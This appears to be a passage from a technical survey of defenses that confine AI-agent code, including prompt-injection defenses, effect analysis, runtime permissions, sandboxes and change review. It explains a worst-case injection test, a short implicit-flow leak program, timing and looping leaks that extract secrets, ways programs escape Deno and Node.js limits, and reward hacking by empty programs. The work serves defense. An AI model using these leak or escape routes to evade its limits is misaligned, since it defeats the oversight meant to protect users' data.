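Zhou and colleagues tested this on AgentDojo's Slack tasks, which pair 21 user tasks with 5 attacks to make 105 combinations. All four of their models resisted every attack even with the policy off, so the ordinary benchmark couldn't show whether the policy helped. They therefore simulated a worst case. Whenever a model received data containing the attacker's text, they removed the real task and left only that data as the prompt, so that the model acted on the attacker's instructions. They ran the 105 combinations seven times,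 for 735 trials per model:

| Model | Injections resisted without the policy | With it | Tasks completed without the policy | With it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

The policy stopped every injection, but the models completed only 40–48% of the tasks with it, compared with 67–76% without. The perfect score also depends partly on the researchers' judgement. AgentDojo had counted 29 of the 2,940 trials as successful attacks because the agent opened a certain web address, but Zhou and colleagues reviewed these by hand and found no violation, since opening the address revealed nothing. The 735 trials are seven repetitions of 105 combinations, so they are weaker evidence about other kinds of attack than 735 different combinations would be.

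### Tracking data in a separate interpreter

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, is the baseline for the other systems. One model writes a program from the user's request without seeing any untrusted data. A second model reads that data but can't use tools. CaMeL runs the program in its own interpreter for a restricted form of Python, which tracks where each value came from and checks a policy before each tool call. An instruction hidden in a file can't change the program, because the first model writes the program before the file is opened.

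Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found a gap in how the interpreter tracks values. Adapted to the sales program, their example works like this:

```
flag = true
big  = true
if total > 1000000:
    flag = false
if flag:
    big = false
if big:
    post(STRANGER, "big month")
```

In a month with sales above a million, the program sets `flag` to false, and the interpreter marks `flag` as secret because the total decided its value. The program then skips `big = false`, so the interpreter doesn't mark `big` as secret and lets the message go out. In a month with lower sales, `big` becomes false and the program sends nothing, so the stranger can tell whether sales exceeded a million. LIO would refuse the message, because reading the total changes the label for everything that follows. TACIT would allow the comparison only inside `map`, where a function can't change an outside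 variable.

Odersky and colleagues object that CaMeL doesn't let agents define their own functions, and that it stops tracking data once the data enters a model's conversation as ordinary text. The second objection is weaker than it sounds, because CaMeL keeps untrusted data away from the model that writes the program.

### How much usefulness each system loses

Zhou and colleagues argue that writing the whole program in advance makes CaMeL less useful, because many tasks require an agent to look at some data before deciding what to do. In their tests without attacks, ELBA completed 8–10 of the 21 Slack tasks with its policy on, depending on the model, and CaMeL completed 4–6. The difference is uncertain with so few tasks, and one of their 95% intervals runs from −7 to +34 percentage points. In earlier figures, which Garby and colleagues cite under ELBA's former name, ELBA completed 8 tasks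 and CaMeL completed 7. ELBA took about three times as long to run as CaMeL, because its agents call the model again as they read.

Odersky and colleagues set TACIT's results on AgentDojo beside those that CaMeL's developers had published. The figures are the share of user tasks completed:

| Model | System | Banking | Office | Slack | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% |
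| | TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% |
| | TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% |

The paper describes TACIT's scores as comparable to CaMeL's. That is generous for the o4-mini-high results, where TACIT did worse than CaMeL in all four areas and trailed by 28 points on office tasks. With Gemini, TACIT led by a wide margin on travel tasks because CaMeL failed nearly all of them.

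Garby and colleagues built a third rival, an agent called Randori, and compared it with CaMeL on the banking tasks. With its policy on, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 runs with each of two models, about half as many as with the policy off. Randori completed roughly twice as many as CaMeL did with its policy on, and resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks. It completed more runs mainly because of a feature called endorsement, which lets a program mark untrusted data as trusted at a visible point in the code. When the researchers removed endorsement, Randori completed noticeably fewer tasks.

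They also divided the 144 combinations of banking task and attack into two groups. In 97, the attack needs a tool that a program written in advance would never call, so CaMeL and Randori can resist it without checking labels. Only the other 47 test data tracking. TACIT and ELBA let a model write more code after it has read the data, so their defense in all 144 would depend on types and labels.

These comparisons don't settle which system loses least. Each comes from a team that built one of the competitors, and the tasks, models and policies differ. The most direct comparison is Zhou and colleagues' own, in which ELBA lost about four in ten of the tasks it had completed once the policy was switched on, and CaMeL lost about two thirds. Some of these losses are unavoidable. Garby and colleagues quote ELBA's developers as saying that many tasks "involve flows that no secure policy would admit".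 For example, a user may ask an agent to do whatever a web page says, which is what the policy exists to prevent. But any of these systems could run the monthly sales report if its policy let the accounts department receive the total.

### Leaks that remain

None of these systems hides how long a program takes. A function inside TACIT's `map` can't send anything, but it could run for ten seconds if the file mentions a certain customer and finish at once if it doesn't. Anyone who notices the delay learns whether the file mentions that customer. Odersky and colleagues leave such leaks outside their guarantee. Whoever runs the program could hold every result until a fixed time after the start, but then every program would take as long as the slowest.

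A program can also leak by never finishing. Stefan and colleagues give the example of a function that loops forever if a secret review contains certain text and returns normally otherwise. LIO's guarantee doesn't cover this kind of leak, although clearance prevents it when the program has no reason to read the secret. One run reveals only a yes or a no, which may not matter much, but 30 such answers are enough to reveal a nine-digit account number. Garby and colleagues note that CaMeL automatically reruns programs that fail, in a loop that its tracking doesn't cover. An attacker could use this loop to extract a whole secret, one answer at a time. Limiting reruns therefore protects secrets as well as saving money.

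Data that the user chooses to release is harder to deal with. In both of Randori's failures, the user had asked it to pay whatever a file said to pay, and the attacker had replaced the file. The program had to endorse the file's contents as trustworthy to do the task. Blocking the attack would have meant refusing all such payments or relying on a model to notice that the text was suspicious. The damage is limited, though. Garby and colleagues gave a machine-checked proof that endorsing data doesn't weaken the protection of secrets.

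The sales total also releases information about customers, since in a month with a single sale it is the amount that one customer paid. If the generated program calculates the number that `sendTotal` releases, it can also hide other data in that number. A number of up to 12 digits can hold about 40 bits, enough to spell an eight-letter name. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests labelling each output with an estimate of how much information about the secret it carries. This could flag a total with too many digits, but not one that hides a short code. For a monthly report, it would be safer for people to write `addUp` and to let `sendTotal` accept only its result. The generated program would then still decide when to send the total, but would not control what the number contains.

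## Enforcing the list in languages without effect types

Models write most of their code in Python, JavaScript and Unix shell, none of which has effect types. Whoever runs the code can still search it for effects beforehand, block operations as the program attempts them, or hold back its file changes until someone has reviewed them.

### Following calls through the code

Software can estimate a program's effects from its code even when the types don't record them. Google's *Capslock* (2023) does this for Go, a typed language without effect types. It traces the calls from each function in a package, through the package's dependencies, to categorized operations in Go's standard library. Google built it for programmers who use other people's packages and want to know, for example, whether a logging library can run other programs. It works just as well on packages written by a model.

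Capslock calls its categories capabilities, although they are names on a fixed list, like Linux's. In a May 2024 version of the documentation, Google defines fifteen names. Two of them, `SAFE` and `UNSPECIFIED`, control the analysis itself, and the other thirteen describe what the code may do:

| Capability | What it covers |
|---|---|
| `FILES` | Reading, writing, creating and deleting files, and changing who may use them |
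| `NETWORK` | Connecting to other computers and accepting connections |
| `READ_SYSTEM_STATE` | Reading environment variables, network addresses and similar details |
| `MODIFY_SYSTEM_STATE` | Changing environment variables or the current folder |
| `RUNTIME` | Reading or changing sensitive settings of Go's own runtime |
| `OPERATING_SYSTEM` | Anything in Go's `os` package without a category of its own |
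| `EXEC` | Running other programs |
| `SYSTEM_CALLS` | Making requests directly to the kernel |
| `ARBITRARY_EXECUTION` | Running assembly code, or breaking Go's type rules |
| `CGO` | Calling code written in C |
| `UNSAFE_POINTER` | Handling memory in ways that can break the type rules |
| `REFLECT` | Using reflection |
| `UNANALYZED` | Calls that Capslock couldn't follow |

`FILES` covers both reading and deleting, so Capslock would report the same categories for the sales program and for the version that deletes its input. The list also has no category for the clock or random numbers. Its default is good, though. Everything in the `os` package counts as `OPERATING_SYSTEM` unless the developers have assigned it to another category, so an operation they overlooked still appears in the report.

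The last seven rows cover code that could do almost anything or that Capslock can't analyze. Reflection, for example, usually does something simple, such as reading the fields of a record, but Google's *Using Capslock* points out that it can also call any function. Capslock reports `REFLECT` unless it can establish that a particular use is harmless. It can't analyze C or assembly code, so it reports calls to that code as `CGO` or `ARBITRARY_EXECUTION`. Because these cases have their own categories, a grant can exclude them, much as Safe Haskell rejects unsafe features.

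Capslock has no category for code that might let two parts of a Go program change the same variable at the same time. Such changes can corrupt memory and cause any behavior at all, but according to Google's *Caveats*, Capslock doesn't report code that might make them. A clean report is therefore good evidence about a program whose author is honest, but it doesn't guarantee that an author who is trying to hide something has failed.

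### Reading a report

In August 2022, an attacker copied thousands of projects on the code-sharing site GitHub and added a short malicious function to them. The function posted the computer's environment variables to a server and ran any commands that came back. Google's *Examples* gives Capslock's report on the Go version of this function, and also its report on Capslock's own code:

| Capability | Calls in the malicious function | Calls in Capslock |
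|---|---|---|
| `EXEC` | 1 | 1 |
| `FILES` | 1 | 2 |
| `NETWORK` | 1 | 0 |
| `READ_SYSTEM_STATE` | 1 | 2 |
| `MODIFY_SYSTEM_STATE` | 2 | 0 |
| `OPERATING_SYSTEM` | 1 | 1 |
| `REFLECT` | 1 | 2 |
| `UNANALYZED` | 1 | 2 |
| `UNSAFE_POINTER` | 0 | 2 |

The malicious function has eight capabilities and the harmless tool has seven, and they share six. The number of capabilities is therefore a poor warning sign unless a reviewer also considers the program's size and purpose. Many ordinary programs have eight capabilities, but that is a lot for a function of about twenty lines.

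To find out why a capability is in the report, a reviewer can ask for an example of the calls that lead to it. For `EXEC` in Capslock's own code, a shortened version is:

```
main -> LoadPackages -> packages.Load -> defaultDriver
     -> findExternalDriver -> Cmd.Run
```

Capslock loads the code it analyzes with a standard Go component that can start a helper program. Capslock's call chains are easy to misread. For example, Google attributes `OPERATING_SYSTEM` to a data-encoding library, but the chain shown for it never enters that library. It goes through the same loading component and ends at an operation that kills a process.

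The reports also contain false alarms. The malicious function never opens a file itself, but Capslock reports `FILES`, probably because the function reads the server's reply with a general operation that also works on files, and the analysis counts every type of value that operation might receive. Capslock could report extra capabilities for a Go version of the sales program in the same way, and the program would then be rejected under a grant of only `FILES` and `NETWORK`.

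Capslock doesn't stop anything by itself. A separate tool, depcaps, compares its results with a set of allowed capabilities, which amounts to checking whether E ⊆ G. Another option is to review only the capabilities that a new version adds. *Bringing Capslock analysis to deps.dev* (McClintock and Dethridge) reports that fewer than 2% of new package versions added a capability, so a reviewer would have little to read. By contrast, 9% of Go packages could reach, through some other package, the operations for running other programs. If a model rewrites the sales program every month, comparing each version with the last would reveal a new `EXEC` capability, but someone still has to judge the first version.

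Capslock's *Know what your dependencies can do* lists an experimental Rust version and a Java version, but none for Python or JavaScript. Python and JavaScript are harder to analyze because a program can call a function by a name it builds as text, or replace a function while running. An analyzer has to either miss some effects or assume the worst so often that it rejects many harmless programs.

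### Finding out what a tool does

Agents also call tools that other people wrote, and a model usually has only a tool's written description. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) discusses a tool that is described as writing text to a file but also sends usage statistics over the network. Someone working on private code would want to know this before using the tool.

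The system, developed at Brown University, analyzes the tool's code to produce a summary called a synopsis. For the tool in the example, the synopsis shows that the path affects a file write, and that the content affects both a file write and a network write. Unlike a list of categories, it shows which input may influence which effect. The user's software compares the synopsis with a policy before each call. If the policy forbids network writes while the user is working on sensitive code, the software refuses the call.

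Like a compiler, the analysis can't always tell which folder a program will use. The tool's developer therefore replaces each ordinary operation, such as writing a file, with a version that checks the path or host against limits sent with the call. A second analysis verifies that every effect goes through one of these checked operations and that the tool can't alter the limits, so the user doesn't have to trust that the developer did this properly.

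Adam and colleagues built a prototype for tools written in Rust and tested it on wanted and harmful versions of three programming tasks: saving an access key, editing private code, and publishing a project. In the harmful versions, the agent saved the key in the wrong folder instead of the project folder, edited the code with a tool that secretly sent statistics, and published a project whose settings file contained a secret key.

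| Protection | Saving a key | Editing private code | Publishing a project |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | Allowed both versions | Allowed both | Allowed both |
| Anthropic's sandbox with one fixed policy | Blocked both | Allowed both | Allowed both |
| Code analysis alone | Blocked both | Blocked only the harmful version | Blocked only the harmful version |
| Code analysis and checked operations | Blocked only the harmful version | Blocked only the harmful version | Blocked only the harmful version |

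Anthropic's sandbox blocked even the version of the first task that the user wanted, because the user had also asked the agent to edit `.bashrc`, a settings file that the sandbox's fixed policy protected. Code analysis by itself also blocked this version, because the tool might have written anywhere.

Adam and colleagues tested only six cases, which they chose themselves, and they added the hidden statistics to the tool. They also supplied a suitable policy for each task, which may be the hardest part in practice. The test shows that the combination can make distinctions that the alternatives can't, but it doesn't measure how often the combination would make the right ones. Adam and colleagues give no running times. A complete version would also need a way to prove that a remote server is running the code that the analysis examined.

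### Run-time permissions in Deno and Node.js

Deno and Node.js run JavaScript outside a browser, and both can check operations as a program attempts them. Deno denies most access to the outside world by default. Node.js restricts a program only if the person starting it adds `--permission`. In both systems, that person grants categories with flags, which are options typed after the command:

| What the program may do | Deno | Node.js |
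|---|---|---|
| Read files | `--allow-read` | `--allow-fs-read` |
| Write files | `--allow-write` | `--allow-fs-write` |
| Use the network | `--allow-net` | `--allow-net` |
| Start processes | `--allow-run` | `--allow-child-process` |
| Use environment variables | `--allow-env` | No flag |
| Read details of the system | `--allow-sys` | No flag |
| Import code from elsewhere | `--allow-import` | No flag |
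| Load native code | `--allow-ffi` | `--allow-addons`, `--allow-ffi` |
| Start worker threads | No flag | `--allow-worker` |
| Run WASI modules | No flag | `--allow-wasi` |
| Load keys through OpenSSL's loaders | No flag | `--allow-openssl-store` |

Native code is already compiled for the processor, and worker threads let a program do several things at once. Node.js's `--permission` flag also turns off the inspector, a debugging interface.

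The smallest grant for the sales program in Deno uses two of the eight categories, each with a scope:

```
deno run --no-prompt --allow-read=/reports/sales.csv
         --allow-net=accounts.example sales.js
```

With these settings, Deno blocks code from deleting `sales.csv`, reading the payroll or contacting a stranger's server. Without `--no-prompt`, Deno may ask the user to approve a forbidden operation, and many people approve such requests without reading them. Deno also has a matching `--deny` flag for each category, and a denial overrides a grant, so a manager could grant access to a whole folder and exclude part of it.

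The Node.js command is similar:

```
node --permission --allow-fs-read=/reports/sales.csv
     --allow-fs-read=/jobs/sales.js --allow-net /jobs/sales.js
```

The additional read permission is for the program's own file. An example in the Node.js manual shows the error that occurs without this permission. The error message includes the missing permission and the file, so it is easy to see what to add. In this command, `--allow-net` doesn't specify a host, so the program could also post to a stranger's server.

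The Node.js command also leaves environment variables open, so the program should start with an environment that contains no secrets.

### Permissions that let a program escape

Deno's other limits don't apply to whatever a program starts using `--allow-run`, because Deno can check only what happens inside its own runtime. A new process has its own permissions, so if the sales program may start another copy of Deno, it can start that copy with every permission. Starting a shell is just as dangerous. Limiting the permission to one trusted program, as in `--allow-run=git`, is better, but the manager then has to know everything that program can do.

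Deno's `--allow-ffi` flag, which lets a program call native code, similarly lets it read files and open connections that its other permissions don't allow. Deno checks permissions in the layer that runs JavaScript, and native code can make requests to the kernel without going through that layer.

Node.js has the same weaknesses. According to the manual for version 22.14, the limits don't carry over to a new Node.js process or a worker thread. Node.js describes a newer flag for loading encryption keys, `--allow-openssl-store`, as granting broad authority, because the loaders it permits may use files, devices and the network regardless of the other flags.

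Some gaps exist even without a dangerous flag. According to the manual for version 24.4, Node.js follows symbolic links even when they lead outside the permitted folders. A program can also use already-open files without a permission check, and some start-up options read files before the checks begin. Whoever starts the program controls the links and the start-up options, so a careful person can close these gaps by giving the program a clean folder.

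The Node.js project presents its permission model as protection against mistakes in trusted code and doesn't promise it will stop malicious code. The model's flags are worth using for a program that nobody has read and that a prompt injection may have influenced, but they shouldn't be the only barrier.

### Starting with no access

Deno and Node.js have built-in file and network operations, which they have to block. A safer design is to run the program in an environment that has no such operations until someone supplies them.

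WebAssembly is a compact format for compiled programs that can run inside other software. A WebAssembly module can calculate and use its own memory, but it can access anything else only by calling functions that its host, the software running it, supplies. WASI, the WebAssembly System Interface, is a standard set of these functions for using resources such as files, clocks, random numbers and network connections. The host chooses which functions a module receives, and can give it access to one folder instead of the whole disk.

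The sales module would receive an interface for reading from `/reports` and another for sending web requests. The host could restrict the module further by supplying only the `read_sales` and `send_total` operations from the Haskell version. Python code has to run in a Python interpreter compiled to WebAssembly.

Monty, a small Python interpreter that the software company Pydantic wrote for running code from models, avoids that step. A program in Monty starts without access to files, environment variables or the network, and can call only the outside functions that its host passes in. The sales program would run almost unchanged if the host supplied `read_file` and `post`. But Monty supports only part of Python, so a model that relied on a popular data-analysis library would have to write the calculation another way.

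With either system, the effect list is the set of functions that the host supplies. The list can be very short, but how much each function allows depends on the host's code. A `read_file` that accepts any path would let the program read any file the host can read, and a function for running shell commands would let it run any command the host can run. A bug in the interpreter could also let a program get around the list.

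### Sandboxes around coding agents

Coding agents need to run compilers, tests and other people's software, which a small interpreter can't do, so their makers often put every command in a sandbox that the operating system enforces. The sandbox also covers any program that a command starts, so permission to start processes no longer lets code get around the other limits.

These sandboxes usually offer only a few modes. In 2025, OpenAI's Codex had three: read-only, workspace-write (which also let the agent change files in the project folder), and full access. In the first two, commands had no network access unless the user allowed it. Anthropic's sandbox instead has separate settings for files and the network.

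Codex's three modes are easy to remember, but none matches the grant {FileRead, Net}. Read-only mode stops the sales program from posting its total. Workspace-write mode with the network turned on lets it post, but also lets it overwrite `sales.csv` if the file is in the project folder. When each mode permits everything the previous one does, a program that needs one permission often has to be given others it doesn't need. Separate settings avoid this but require one more decision.

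An operating-system sandbox also has little information about the task. Zhou and colleagues point out that it confines a process to a fixed set of folders, whereas a capability in a programming language can become narrower as the program runs. A capability can also represent something that has no equivalent in the operating system, such as the files on one branch of a project's history.

Many agents also check the text of each shell command, but this is unreliable because the text may not show what the command will do. It is also an awkward way to express a policy because, as Zhou and colleagues observe, users usually want to say which files an agent may change, not which commands it may run. A list of commands is useful for deciding when to ask the user, but the sandbox should enforce the limit.

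### Reviewing changes before they become permanent

A manager who can't decide in advance which files a program should change may find it easier to judge the changes after it runs. *Controlling Opaque-Component Effects with Semisolates and Ef*, by Lamprou, Zhu and colleagues, presents a Linux tool that allows this for a program in any language. Typing `ef` before a command runs it with a private view of the computer's files. When the command ends, `ef` lists the changes and asks whether to apply them.

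The private view has two layers. The lower layer is the real file system, which the program can read but not change. When the program modifies a file, the new version goes into a temporary upper layer. When it deletes a file, a marker in the upper layer hides the original. The program sees both layers as a single set of files, so it behaves as if its changes were real. Applying the changes copies or moves them to the real file system, and discarding them leaves the original files as they were.

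If the sales program deleted `sales.csv` under `ef`, the deletion would appear in the list of changes and the manager could reject it. The manager could also accept some changes and reject others, or hide the payroll from the program before starting it. But `ef` doesn't hold back network messages, so if the program posts a total or a customer list, it is sent before the manager sees the list. An option turns off the network, but then the sales program can't send its report and a trusted program has to do it.

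Lamprou and colleagues compared running times with and without `ef` on 23 tasks. Five were scripts that ChatGPT had written for jobs such as compressing files and searching a log, and these took 1.1 to 1.9 times as long under `ef`. Across all 23 tasks, the range was 1.0 to 8.3 times. The largest slowdowns were in very short commands, such as copying a file, which `ef` was also tracing in detail. For a short program, most of the added time goes to setting up and removing the private view. A command that printed a few words took 165 milliseconds in total, which is too short to notice when running a monthly report.

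They also found `ef` to be 1.3 to 225.7 times as fast as Docker, a widely used container system. The largest differences arose partly because they copied the input files into each container and the results back out, while `ef` reads the originals in place. Giving a container direct access to the real folder would avoid the copying but remove the chance to reject changes.

The list of changes can be too long to read. Installing any of the four JavaScript packages tested created between 7,391 and 8,565 files. An add-on to `ef` uses a language model to summarize the changes, which is convenient, but the user has to trust that the summary leaves out nothing important. Rules that accept changes only in certain folders are safer, because software can easily check every change against them, even when there are thousands.

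Lamprou and colleagues designed `ef` to guard against accidents, and they exclude malicious programs written to get around it. Their tests did include packages whose past versions had contained real attacks, but those attackers had no reason to expect `ef`. A prompt injection could lead a model to write code that deliberately evades it. `ef` is therefore best suited to catching mistakes, such as a clean-up command that deletes the wrong folder, and it needs a sandbox around it when the program may be hostile.

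### Choosing a combination

The methods fail in different ways, so using two together gives more protection than either alone. The sales program could run under Deno with the two scoped permissions, inside an operating-system sandbox that allows access only to the same folder and server. Deno would let the program read `sales.csv` but not overwrite it, and the sandbox would still limit any native code or new process that bypassed Deno's checks. Neither checks what a message contains, so `send_total` would still be useful.

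| Method | When it checks | What it can see | What it costs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Capslock | Before the program runs | Categories that Go code might use, but not which files or hosts | False alarms, and time to read chains of calls |
| Adam and colleagues' prototype | Before and during each tool call | A tool's possible effects, then the actual path or host | Developers must change their tools; no running times reported |
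| Deno and Node.js permissions | At each operation | Operations in JavaScript, but not what native code or new processes do | A refusal can stop a program halfway |
| WASI and Monty | At each call to the host | Only calls to functions that the host supplied | Someone must write those functions, and some existing code won't run |
| Operating-system sandboxes | At each request to the kernel | File and network access by the program and everything it starts, but not its purpose | Few modes, so often more excess authority |
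| `ef` | After the program runs, before its changes become permanent | Changes to files, but not the contents of messages already sent | 1.1 to 1.9 times the running time for ChatGPT's scripts, and time to review the changes |

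## Getting a model to write programs that fit the list

A checker that rejects unsafe programs is of little use if models can't write safe ones that pass. The model has to do its task in code that compiles and uses only the permissions it was granted, often in a language it has seen less of than Python. In tests of TACIT, which checks an agent's Scala code, these requirements caused little or no drop in performance. The drop can be much larger in a language the model barely knows, though giving the model documentation and error messages recovers a good part of it.

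### Compile, read the error, try again

The usual method is a loop. The model receives the task, the operations it may call and the grant. It writes a program, and the compiler checks it. If the check fails, the model receives the error and writes another version. This repeats until a version passes or the model runs out of attempts.

For the sales program, the model might receive this interface:

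```
read_file : Text -> Text            \ {FileRead}
post      : (Address, Text) -> Text \ {Net}
grant     : {FileRead, Net}
```

Suppose its first draft also saves a copy of the total:

```
text  = read_file("sales.csv")
total = add_up(text)
write_file("total.txt", to_text(total))
reply = post(ACCOUNTS_ADDRESS, "Total sales: " + to_text(total))
```

The compiler could then return this error:

```
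line 3: write_file needs FileWrite
this program may use only FileRead and Net
```

The model deletes the third line, and the second draft passes. The first draft never ran, so the mistake only required one more attempt. A run-time failure is harder to recover from. If a program posts the total and then crashes, and the model corrects it and reruns it from the top, the accounts department receives the same total twice.

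In Odersky and colleagues' customer-service tests of TACIT, the prompt lists every data type and function, tells the model to read any error and try again, and forbids it to fall back on calling tools directly.

Many of the errors had nothing to do with safety. A dollar sign in a Scala text template introduces a variable, so a program that reports a total of $50 has to write `$$50`, and agents often left out the second dollar sign. Another error came from a harmless function that printed the first five lines of a file. The model had declared the parameter as a plain `FileEntry`, which in Scala's capture checking means a value that holds no capability, but an open file holds one. Changing the type to `FileEntry^` fixes the error.

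Compiler messages are meant for programmers, and some of them suggest loosening the rules. When an agent's code used a value that might be missing, the compiler suggested handling the missing case, asserting that the value is there, or importing a feature called `unsafeNulls`. A system for generated code should remove suggestions that loosen the rules, such as importing `unsafeNulls`, from these messages.

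Protecting secrets also makes the loop less effective. If code fails while processing data in TACIT's `Classified` container, TACIT hides the error message because it might reveal the data. The program then appears to succeed, and the user gets an empty answer. TACIT therefore prompts the model to return a message such as "No matching transaction" instead of raising an error in that code.

### What the typed interface did to performance

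Odersky and colleagues compared agents that wrote typed Scala with agents that called tools in the ordinary way. One benchmark, τ²-bench, simulates customers who want to change a flight or return an order. The table gives the share of tasks completed, averaged over ten runs of each:

| Model | Airline, ordinary tools | Airline, typed Scala | Retail, ordinary tools | Retail, typed Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
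| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Typed Scala did better in all six comparisons, by 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points. Odersky and colleagues credit the compiler's error messages and the use of structured results instead of raw JSON text.

That is plausible, but the experiment changed two things at once. The Scala agents wrote programs, which can combine several operations in one step, while the others made separate calls. A third group that wrote ordinary Python would have shown how much of the gain came from types. The customer-service functions are also simple. `cancelReservation`, for example, takes a reservation number and returns a reservation, and its printed signature mentions no capability. The test therefore shows that models can write typed Scala, but it may be weak evidence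 of how well they handle capture sets.

The other benchmark, SWE-bench Lite, consists of 300 real software faults to repair. MiniMax M2.5 fixed 41.7% of them when it had to request access to files and commands through TACIT's library, and 43.3% with ordinary tools. The difference is five faults, which could easily be chance. Odersky and colleagues suggest that repair work relies on Unix shell habits that are harder to express through their library.

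Retries were rare on τ²-bench. Between 0.32% and 7.93% of the programs needed any, and those programs needed 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. DeepSeek needed the most on the airline tasks, about 11 retries per 100 programs. Compiling took less than a second, so most of the time spent on retries was the model's.

The comparison covers only three models on τ²-bench and one on SWE-bench Lite. Claude Sonnet 4.6, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high appear only in the paper's safety tests, which don't compare typed Scala with ordinary tool calls. The comparison also doesn't cover models much smaller than these.

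### Languages that models have rarely seen

Scala is fairly well known, although its capture checking is new. An organisation that wants a language with a better effect list may have to choose one with far less public code for models to learn from.

In *No Resource, No Benchmarks, No Problem?*, Giagnorio, Martin-Lopez and Bavota (2026) gave four models the same tasks in nine languages, including Gleam and MoonBit, which both had their first stable releases in 2024. On the hardest tasks, the models solved 59–89% in Python and Java but at most about 1% in Gleam and MoonBit. Most failures in the two new languages were syntax errors, including about two thirds of GPT-4o's.

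Models did much better in moderately rare languages. OpenAI's o3-mini solved 84% of the hardest tasks in Haskell and 89% in Python, although GitHub had about 140 times as many Python projects as Haskell projects. A weaker model, Qwen 3, solved 27% in Haskell and 70% in Python. This suggests that a capable model can work in Haskell even though less public Haskell code exists.

These models are now old, and in that comparison they had one attempt and no documentation. Shen, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Bridging the Knowledge Void*, gave newer models both documentation and a way to run their code. The language was Cangjie, a statically typed language first released in June 2024, and the table shows the share of 155 tasks solved:

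| Model | No help | Repeated searches of the documentation | Documentation, compiler and sample tests |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 3% | 47% | 63% |
| Qwen3-Max | 8% | 53% | 74% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 45% | 66% | 82% |

When Shen and colleagues took away Qwen3-Max's ability to run code, its score fell from 74% to 54%. Taking away its documentation search had the same effect. A new effect-typed language therefore needs good reference pages as well as good error messages. Even with nothing taken away, 14% of Claude's final programs didn't compile. The compiler would stop these programs before they did any harm, but their tasks would remain undone.

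Some models gain more from the loop than others. *Frontier Coding Agents Use Metaprogramming to Adapt to Unfamiliar Programming Languages* (Sharma, Thorat and Chopra, 2026) tested six agents on four deliberately strange languages, such as Brainfuck, which has eight one-character commands. Scores ranged from 11.3% for Kimi K2.5 to 99.7% for GPT-5.4 on a high reasoning setting, although the agents' scores were within seven points of each other on a standard test of software repair. Letting the agents run more trial programs helped Claude Opus 4.6 but left the smaller Claude Haiku 4.5 near zero on Brainfuck and Befunge-98.

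The weaker agents benefited from working code but barely from written advice. Claude Sonnet 4.6 solved 12 of 80 Brainfuck problems both with and without a description of Opus's strategy. With a small library of helper functions taken from the strongest agents' work, it solved 64. Haiku rose only from 4 to 7. For an effect-typed language, this is a reason to give the model tested functions and short examples that compile rather than a longer explanation of the type system. The benefit would probably be smaller, because practical effect systems are much less unusual than Brainfuck.

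The strongest agents often wrote Python programs that generated Brainfuck instead of writing Brainfuck directly. When Sharma and colleagues forbade this, Opus fell from 64 solved problems to 27, and GPT-5.4 from 79 to 29. An agent that did the same with an effect-typed language would run Python that hadn't been checked for effects, and this Python could read the payroll even if the final program couldn't. The agent's workspace therefore needs its own sandbox, unless the agent can run only checked code.

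### Training models and constraining their output

An organisation that controls its own model can train it for the language. Giagnorio and colleagues trained an open model further on public Gleam and MoonBit code, then restored its ability to follow instructions by adding the difference between the weights of two existing versions of the model. This raised its score on the hardest tasks to more than 25%.

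Reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for programs that work, needs fewer examples. Boruch-Gruszecki, Zi and colleagues (2025) built *Agnostics*, a system that rewards the model only if its program produces the right output for each test input. The same tests therefore work for any language, and adding a language takes a configuration file of four or five lines. They used it on Lua, Julia, R, OCaml and Fortran, and report that a model with 4 billion parameters rivalled open models with 16 to 70 billion.

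A model that almost never writes a valid program gets almost no rewards to learn from. *Selective Left-Shift* (2026) cites syntax errors as one reason reinforcement learning works poorly in rare programming languages. Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues addressed this by adding advice about common mistakes to the prompt, and found that a starting success rate of 0.09% was enough.

*Reinforcement Learning from Compiler and Language Server Feedback* (2025) proposes rewards after each step, based on what the compiler and similar tools report. When Boruch-Gruszecki and colleagues partially rewarded programs that ran without errors but gave wrong answers, the models were very likely to exploit this, for example by writing empty programs. Models would exploit a reward for staying within the grant in the same way. An empty program has no effects and fits every grant, so the reward must also require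 the right result.

Another approach, type-constrained generation, works as the model writes a program piece by piece, blocking any piece that would make a type error unavoidable. In *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models* (2025), this cut the number of programs with compiler errors by 74.8% on one set of tasks and 56.0% on another. Enforcing syntax alone, even perfectly, would have cut it by only 9.0% and 4.8%. Enforcing syntax would probably help much more in a language like Gleam, where most failures are syntax errors.

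The same technique could stop the model from writing a call to `write_file` when the grant lacks `FileWrite`. But the implementation took more than 11,000 lines of code, and the technique needs control over how the model picks each piece, which companies that sell access to their models often don't offer. The finished program should still go through the compiler, because a mistake in the constraint code could let a forbidden call through.

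### Languages designed for models

Some developers have concluded that models need new languages. In *A Language For Agents* (2026), Ronacher concedes that agents do far better in languages they know from training. But he finds that they do passably in Zig, a rare and quickly changing language, when they have the right documentation. He expects new languages to succeed if they keep familiar syntax. Four existing attempts at a language for models check effects to very different degrees.

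AILANG's compiler compares a function's declared effects with the operations it calls. Its developers report a compile rate of 67% for AILANG and about 45% for "Python-style code", based on 264 benchmark runs with GPT-5, Claude Sonnet 4.5 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. The Python figure is surprisingly low, since GPT-4o, an older model, wrote Python that passed all the tests on 78–91% of Giagnorio and colleagues' tasks. Either AILANG's tasks were much harder or "Python-style code" doesn't mean ordinary Python.

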